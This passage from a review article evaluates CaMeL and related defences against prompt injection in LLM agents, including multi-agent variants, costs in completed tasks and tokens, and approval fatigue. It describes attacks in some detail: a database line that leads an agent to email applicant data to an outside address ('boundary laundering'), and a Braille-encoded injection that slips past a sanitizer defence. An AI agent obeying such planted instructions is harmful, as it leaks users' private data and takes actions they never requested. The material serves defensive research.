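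The theorem covers every program in the language, including code that a model writes during a run. Garby and colleagues proved it in Lean, a language for computer-checked proofs, and wrote the interpreter in Lean too, so the proofs apply to the software that calls the model. This removes the kind of tracking errors they found in CaMeL. Developers still have to label data sources correctly and put the right checks on sensitive tools.

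Strict noninterference would make many useful tasks impossible, including paying a bill described in a file. LLMbda therefore has an `endorse` operation that relabels an untrusted value as trusted. The planner decides where to use it before the agent reads any untrusted data. The risk is small if the value must come from a short fixed list. For example, choosing one of eight email categories gives an attacker at most three bits of influence, but an account number has no such limit.

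Garby and colleagues proved that `endorse` can't be used to leak secrets, but it does give up protection against false data. Their agent failed in two of 1,296 attacked runs, both on the false-bill problem, because the plan had endorsed payment details from a file the attacker had replaced. Without `endorse`, the agent blocked the attack but couldn't have paid a genuine bill either. The language doesn't prevent a planner from endorsing too much.

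### Safe agents in an unsafe system

In many systems, one agent now takes the user's request and delegates parts of it to other agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that giving each agent its own CaMeL doesn't protect the whole system.

In one demonstration, an orchestrator agent could call a database agent and a notification agent, and all three ran CaMeL. The user asked for a summary of job applicants' details to be sent to Julie on Slack. An attacker had planted a line in the database asking for the details to be sent to an outside email address as well. Neither the database agent's planner nor the orchestrator's planner saw the records, but the orchestrator's program put the summary text into a message telling the notification agent to send it to Julie via Slack. The notification agent treated the whole message as its user's request, so its planner read the attacker's line as a trusted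 instruction and wrote a plan with an extra call that emailed the data out.

Each agent followed a plan written from input it treated as trusted, so each had control-flow integrity, but the system as a whole did not. Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering. Their experiments used no data-flow policies, but policies based on source tags might not have helped much. The notification agent's planner wrote the outside address directly into its program, so a policy there would probably have treated the address as coming from the user. A fixed list of permitted recipients could still have stopped the email.

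The problem can arise in any system with at least two agents if one of them has a tool that returns untrusted data. If that agent can call another agent, some request will lead it to use the tool and put the result into its instructions to the other. If another agent calls it instead, the caller can receive the untrusted result and put it into a second instruction. Either way, untrusted text reaches a planner. This assumes that the agents are flexible enough to accept such requests, which is usually the reason for having them. Under that assumption, some requests are vulnerable, but not necessarily all.

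Peters-Gill and colleagues' solution, multi-CaMeL, splits each call between agents into two parts. The `message` contains instructions for the receiving planner, and the interpreter rejects it if it depends on any tool's output. Everything that came from a tool goes into `variables`, which the receiving agent's program can use but its planner can't read. Those values keep their tags, so policies can apply across the whole system.

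To test it, they divided AgentDojo's tools among groups of specialised agents and ran all 949 injected cases on five models:

| Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL in each agent | Multi-CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% | 0.0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Average attack success | 12.9% | 0.2% | 0.0% |

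Separate CaMeL agents stopped nearly all the successful attacks, and every attack that still succeeded used boundary laundering. The 0.2% success rate probably understates the danger, because the attack goals came from a benchmark for single agents and nobody adapted the attacks to this defence. The attacks are also a weak test of a strong model, since none succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without a defence. The job applicant demonstration is therefore better evidence of the weakness than the 0.2% rate, and multi-CaMeL's design is a better reason to trust the fix than the absence of successful attacks against it.

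Multi-CaMeL has no retry loop that could leak information, but it extends CaMeL's interpreter and so inherits the skipped-assignment flaw. This flaw could let information from a tool influence a `message` without the interpreter recording that influence. Branch steering also remains possible. If a plan contains two prepared instructions for another agent, untrusted data can determine which one the agent receives.

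## What CaMeL costs in completed tasks, computation and user effort

An agent running CaMeL completes fewer tasks than the same model without it, partly because it plans without seeing any data and partly because its policies block calls the user wanted. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, quote CaMeL's published AgentDojo result with GPT-4o, in which it completed 53.6% (±9.9 points) of harmless tasks and no attack succeeded. In their own test, GPT-4o without a defence completed 83.0% of harmless tasks, but 57.7% of attacks succeeded. GPT-4o is now an old model, and these figures don't separate the tasks lost to planning from those lost to policies. Later tests separate them by including runs with the policies switched off.

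### Planning before seeing the data

Peters-Gill and colleagues used no policies, so the losses they measured come from the planning. They tested on AssetOpsBench, in which an orchestrator agent delegates parts of an industrial maintenance task to four specialised agents, and on MultiAgentDojo, their own multi-agent version of AgentDojo. They removed 29 of AssetOpsBench's 141 tasks because the necessary data didn't exist. The table gives the percentage of harmless tasks completed, with each agent running its own CaMeL.

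| Model | AssetOpsBench, no CaMeL | AssetOpsBench, CaMeL | MultiAgentDojo, no CaMeL | MultiAgentDojo, CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5 | 88.4 | 67.0 | 69.1 | 53.6 |
| GPT-5.5 | 87.5 | 82.1 | 86.6 | 73.2 |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.2 | 64.3 | 78.4 | 38.1 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 75.9 | 55.4 | 76.3 | 42.3 |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 64.3 | 20.5 | 27.8 | 13.4 |

On AssetOpsBench the average loss was 21.6 points. The two strongest models, Fable 5 and GPT-5.5, lost an average of 13.4 points, which Peters-Gill and colleagues take as a sign that better models cope better with CaMeL's constraints. But Fable 5 lost 21.4 points, about as much as the average model, and GPT-5.5 lost 5.4, so of these two only GPT-5.5 supports the claim. The MultiAgentDojo results support it better, since GPT-4.1 lost 40 points there and GPT-5.5 lost 13.

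Fable 5's MultiAgentDojo scores are hard to interpret because the model refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks. Peters-Gill and colleagues suspect that it associated the benchmark with attacks, in which case it might refuse much less in real use. Of the other 45 tasks, Fable 5 completed 41 without CaMeL and 38 with it.

Most of the failures happened because the planner had to commit to a plan before seeing the data. Some tasks needed a tool call that the plan didn't include. In one MultiAgentDojo task, the user asks the agent to look at two people's websites, invite one of them, Dora, to Slack and send both feedback. Dora's email address is on her website. Gemini 2.5 Pro, planning under ordinary CaMeL, guessed an address from the site's name and put the wrong one in the invitation.

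In another run of the same task, this time with multi-CaMeL, the program extracted the right address. But the planner had already written the feedback, which praised the "clean design" of a website that no model had yet read. Peters-Gill and colleagues describe this run as completing the task, so a completion score can leave out some of the ways users are worse off when the planner works without seeing the data.

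A fixed plan can also let substituted data go undetected. In several AssetOpsBench runs, a helper agent couldn't find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for something close instead. The orchestrator had written its program before the reply arrived, and the program continued with the wrong data.

Multi-CaMeL's stricter separation between agents reduces task completion further. The additional drop averaged 3.2 points on AssetOpsBench, but on MultiAgentDojo it was 7.2 points for GPT-5.5 and 15.5 for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

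Planning actions without seeing their results is hardest for agents that operate a computer through its screen. Foerster and colleagues found that plans for these agents needed about 41 tool calls on average, compared with five for AgentDojo. They report that CaMeL kept up to 57% of a frontier model's performance on OSWorld, a benchmark of everyday computer tasks. Claude Sonnet 4.5 without CaMeL had solved 109 tasks that code could check. With CaMeL, it solved 62 of them in at least one of five attempts, but only 31, or 28%, on the first attempt. Reaching 57% therefore requires a way to identify the successful attempt. On a real computer, a failed attempt may also leave changes behind.

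To save time and money, Foerster and colleagues limited the undefended agent in that comparison to 15 steps. It scored 37.7% on OSWorld, against a published 58.1% with 50 steps. They also report that CaMeL improved a small open model, UI-TARS, by up to 19%. That figure uses the best of three attempts for CaMeL, which also had a separate, stronger planner. On a single attempt, the CaMeL version solved 51 of 339 tasks, fewer than the 60 UI-TARS solved alone.

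Better planners helped. When Foerster and colleagues tried nine frontier planners on 17 tasks, GPT-5 completed the most, 12, and weaker planners tended to leave out the fallback branches for unexpected screens. CaMeL should therefore continue to lose fewer tasks to poor planning as models improve, although tasks whose next step depends on content the planner has not seen will remain difficult.

### What the policies add

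Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL with and without its policies on AgentDojo's banking suite, attempting each of the 16 tasks three times. They also attempted 432 runs under attack in each configuration, though many did not finish.

| Model | Policies | Harmless runs completed | Share, with 95% interval | Successful attacks in finished runs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | Off | 32 of 48 | 66.7% ± 23.4 | 1 of 240 |
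| GPT-5.2 | On | 18 of 48 | 37.5% ± 26.6 | 0 of 231 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | Off | 34 of 48 | 70.8% ± 21.4 | 4 of 382 |
| MiMo-v2.5 | On | 18 of 48 | 37.5% ± 26.6 | 0 of 357 |

The intervals are wide because there are only 16 different tasks, and the intervals with policies on and off overlap. Still, both models completed about half as many runs on the same set of tasks with policies on, which is unlikely to be due to chance alone.

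To find out what the policies contributed, Garby and colleagues sorted the suite's 144 pairs of user task and attack goal. In 97 pairs, about two-thirds of the total, the attack needs a tool call or file that a normal plan for the task would never include, so it should fail even without a policy. For example, an attacker who wants the agent to send money fails if the user only asked for a summary of recent transactions. In the other 47 pairs, the plan might already contain the call the attacker needs, so protection depends on checking the values that go into it.

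In practice, most of the other third failed too. With policies off, CaMeL resisted the attack in 279 of 282 runs in the group of 47 pairs. The policies halved the number of completed tasks and stopped five attacks, which would not justify them if this test were the only evidence. But the benchmark's attack goals were written before CaMeL, so the test hardly measures the attack that the policies exist to stop, which is planting false account numbers and addresses. An attacker who knew that the plan was fixed would concentrate on that attack.

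Newer models do not seem to reduce the number of tasks that policies block. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, ran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with four 2026 models. It completed 13 to 17 tasks without policies and four to six with them. With GPT-5.4, the number fell from 17 to five. Turning on strict mode made almost no difference. Even a model that plans perfectly can't complete a task if the policy forbids a step in it.

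Like CaMeL, the system that Zhou and colleagues built completed fewer tasks when they turned its policies on, dropping from 14–18 to 8–10. According to Garby and colleagues, Zhou's team observed that many of the tasks involve data flows "that no secure policy would admit". For example, the benchmark gives an agent credit for posting a stranger's text to a colleague, so an agent whose policy forbids this loses the point.

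How a system handles exceptions also affects how many tasks it completes. The agent that Garby and colleagues built completed 36 of 48 banking runs on GPT-5.2 with its checks always on, twice as many as CaMeL with policies. Their agent enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, and its planner can `endorse` untrusted values. Removing `endorse` reduced completed runs on MiMo-v2.5 from 31 to 26, so `endorse` explains only part of the difference.

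*SecureClaw* (2026), which introduces a rival defence, also reports that CaMeL completed few tasks. Across all four AgentDojo suites, CaMeL completed 29 of 97 harmless tasks and stopped all 629 attacks, while SecureClaw completed 59 of the tasks. The researchers connected CaMeL to the benchmark through an adapter, which may explain some of the tasks it failed to complete.

### Tokens and running time

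CaMeL needs a long prompt to explain its restricted Python, and every failed program means another call to the planner. With GPT-4o on AgentDojo, Bhagwatkar and colleagues measured an average of 13,463 input tokens per task, against 3,764 with no defence, and 1,843 output tokens against 303. The typical task was much cheaper than the average suggests, with a median of 1.8 times the undefended input. (Their text gives 2.82 times for the median, which doesn't match their own table.)

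They also timed CaMeL on the banking and Slack suites against their own defence, the Sanitizer, which uses a language model to rewrite each tool result and remove suspected instructions. On harmless tasks, CaMeL took 839 seconds in total and the Sanitizer took 700. Under attack, CaMeL took 8,417 seconds and the Sanitizer took 3,348.

When Foerster and colleagues adapted CaMeL and Fides to computer use, CaMeL used 1.88 times the tokens of the undefended agent and Fides used 29.6 times. Fides, which Costa and colleagues introduced in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), uses more because it plans one action at a time and calls its planner at every step with the full history. Of 60 tasks, Fides solved 20 on the first attempt, compared with 25 for CaMeL, and 40 within five attempts, compared with 39. The gap in tokens would probably be smaller for short office tasks, which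 have fewer steps and less history to resend.

Small models have more trouble with CaMeL because they often can't write the program it needs. *CapLite* (Xu, Liu and Nakayama, 2026) tested CaMeL on 15 open-weight models, 13 of which had between 1.7 and 12 billion parameters, with the same model in both roles and CaMeL's policies on. For eight models, more than 15% of episodes ended without a program that would run. Granite-4.2-8B had the highest rate, 68%, and returned no code in those episodes. Attempts to repair programs also added model calls. On one Slack task, Qwen3-1.7B made 30 model calls without running a tool.

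| | No defence | CaMeL | CapLite |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmless tasks completed | 59.4% | 24.9% | 28.1% |
| Successful attacks, of 13,935 | 2,322 | 20 | 0 |
| Tokens per episode | 28,000 | 93,700 | 17,100 |

CaMeL remained secure even where it failed to complete tasks, because a program that doesn't run can't do any harm. Three other defences in the study had the model write rules, constraints or plans that determined which calls were allowed. The model's mistakes in writing these let attacks through, with between 214 and 676 successes.

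CapLite, a defence proposed by Xu and colleagues, avoids model-written code. Before the agent reads any data, CapLite's planner chooses every call that changes something. Ordinary software then allows a call only if details such as the recipient and amount appear exactly in the user's request. CapLite uses 18% of the tokens CaMeL does, but it can't loop over records or branch on what it finds. If a user asked it to send Bob a document and his address was only in the meeting notes, it would have to ask the user to confirm the address. On Gemma-4-12B, which writes working CaMeL programs about 97% of the time, CaMeL completed 55.5% of tasks under attack and CapLite 42.0%. CapLite therefore suits small models and simple requests, while a capable planner completes more tasks with CaMeL.

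### Writing policies and answering prompts

CaMeL also requires work from developers that these scores don't measure. Bhagwatkar and colleagues describe its custom interpreter and domain-specific policies as a heavy implementation burden. The benchmark runs used policies that CaMeL's designers had already written for AgentDojo, but a company with its own tools would have to write policies from scratch and revise them whenever a tool changed.

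Software can produce a first draft of the rules. CapLite derives them from each tool's name, description and parameters, treating verbs like "get" as harmless and "send" or "pay" as actions to control. Xu and colleagues compared these rules with labels from a language model. The rules matched the labels on which of AgentDojo's 74 tools only read data, but they treated 17 of 79 arguments as dates or simple settings when the labels marked them as sensitive, including the permission level for sharing a file. A person would still need to review such cases.

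CaMeL requires effort from users when a policy isn't enough to determine whether a call should go ahead. The reruns above count a blocked call as a failure, but a real agent could ask for approval and carry on. That would recover many of the lost tasks, provided users read what they are approving. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* warns that confirmation requests cause fatigue and that people tend to ignore them. If users approve calls by habit, the agent can complete the task but the policy no longer protects them.

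Better planning can reduce the number of approval requests. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) gave several agents the same approval mechanism and measured how much human intervention each needed. On AgentDojo with o4-mini, Fides completed 75.7% of tasks with an approval load of 36.8. Prudentia, whose planner takes the policies into account, completed 73.2% with a load of 19.2. CaMeL could probably use the same approach, since its policies are trusted text that the planner can safely read. Halving the requests would make users more likely to review each one properly, but none of these studies measured how often real users approve an attack.

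### When the undefended model already resists

On MultiAgentDojo, GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks without a defence. Adding CaMeL lowered its task completion rate by 13 percentage points and brought no security benefit that the benchmark could detect. This is a serious argument against CaMeL for someone choosing a defence today.

But the benchmark's attacks are weak, and some of Chen and colleagues' injections succeeded against GPT-5.5. More capable models also aren't automatically more resistant. Of 929 attacks in the CapLite study, six succeeded against the smallest undefended Gemma-4 model and 357 against the 12-billion-parameter version. GPT-5.5's resistance is probably due in large part to training against such attacks, which an attacker can study and work around.

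The Sanitizer is an attractive alternative for the same reason, but it can be bypassed. With GPT-4o it completed 74.1% of harmless AgentDojo tasks, about 20 percentage points more than CaMeL's published figure, and stopped every standard attack. Bhagwatkar and colleagues then tried their own attacks, including a stock injection written in Braille characters. The Sanitizer flagged the encoding as suspicious but translated the message into plain English and passed it on, and the agent booked the hotel that the attacker had named.

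Whether CaMeL is worth using therefore depends on what the agent can do. A well-trained model with a filter is probably enough for an agent that only drafts text for a person to check. But if the agent can pay bills or share private files, one successful attack may do more harm than many failed tasks. Fixing the plan in advance lowers GPT-5.5's task completion rate by 5 to 13 points, which seems reasonable in return for preventing injected text from adding actions. CaMeL's full set of policies is harder to justify everywhere, because it can cause half the tasks or more to fail. Strict policies make more sense for the few tools whose effects can't be undone.

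### Use in products

Google's Chrome browser uses a separate model, the User Alignment Critic, to check each action its agent proposes against the user's request. Google describes the critic as partly inspired by CaMeL. But Chrome's planner still reads web pages, which lets the agent adapt to what it finds but gives up CaMeL's control-flow guarantee. Hostile text on a page can influence the plan, and safety then depends on the critic rejecting the resulting action.

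Ilia Shumailov, one of CaMeL's designers, founded AI Sequrity Company to build defences of this kind. He also co-wrote the multi-agent study by Peters-Gill and colleagues and the computer-use study by Foerster and colleagues. Some of the more favourable evidence on CaMeL's performance and overhead therefore comes from people with a commercial interest in the design. Most of the less favourable evidence comes from researchers presenting competing designs.
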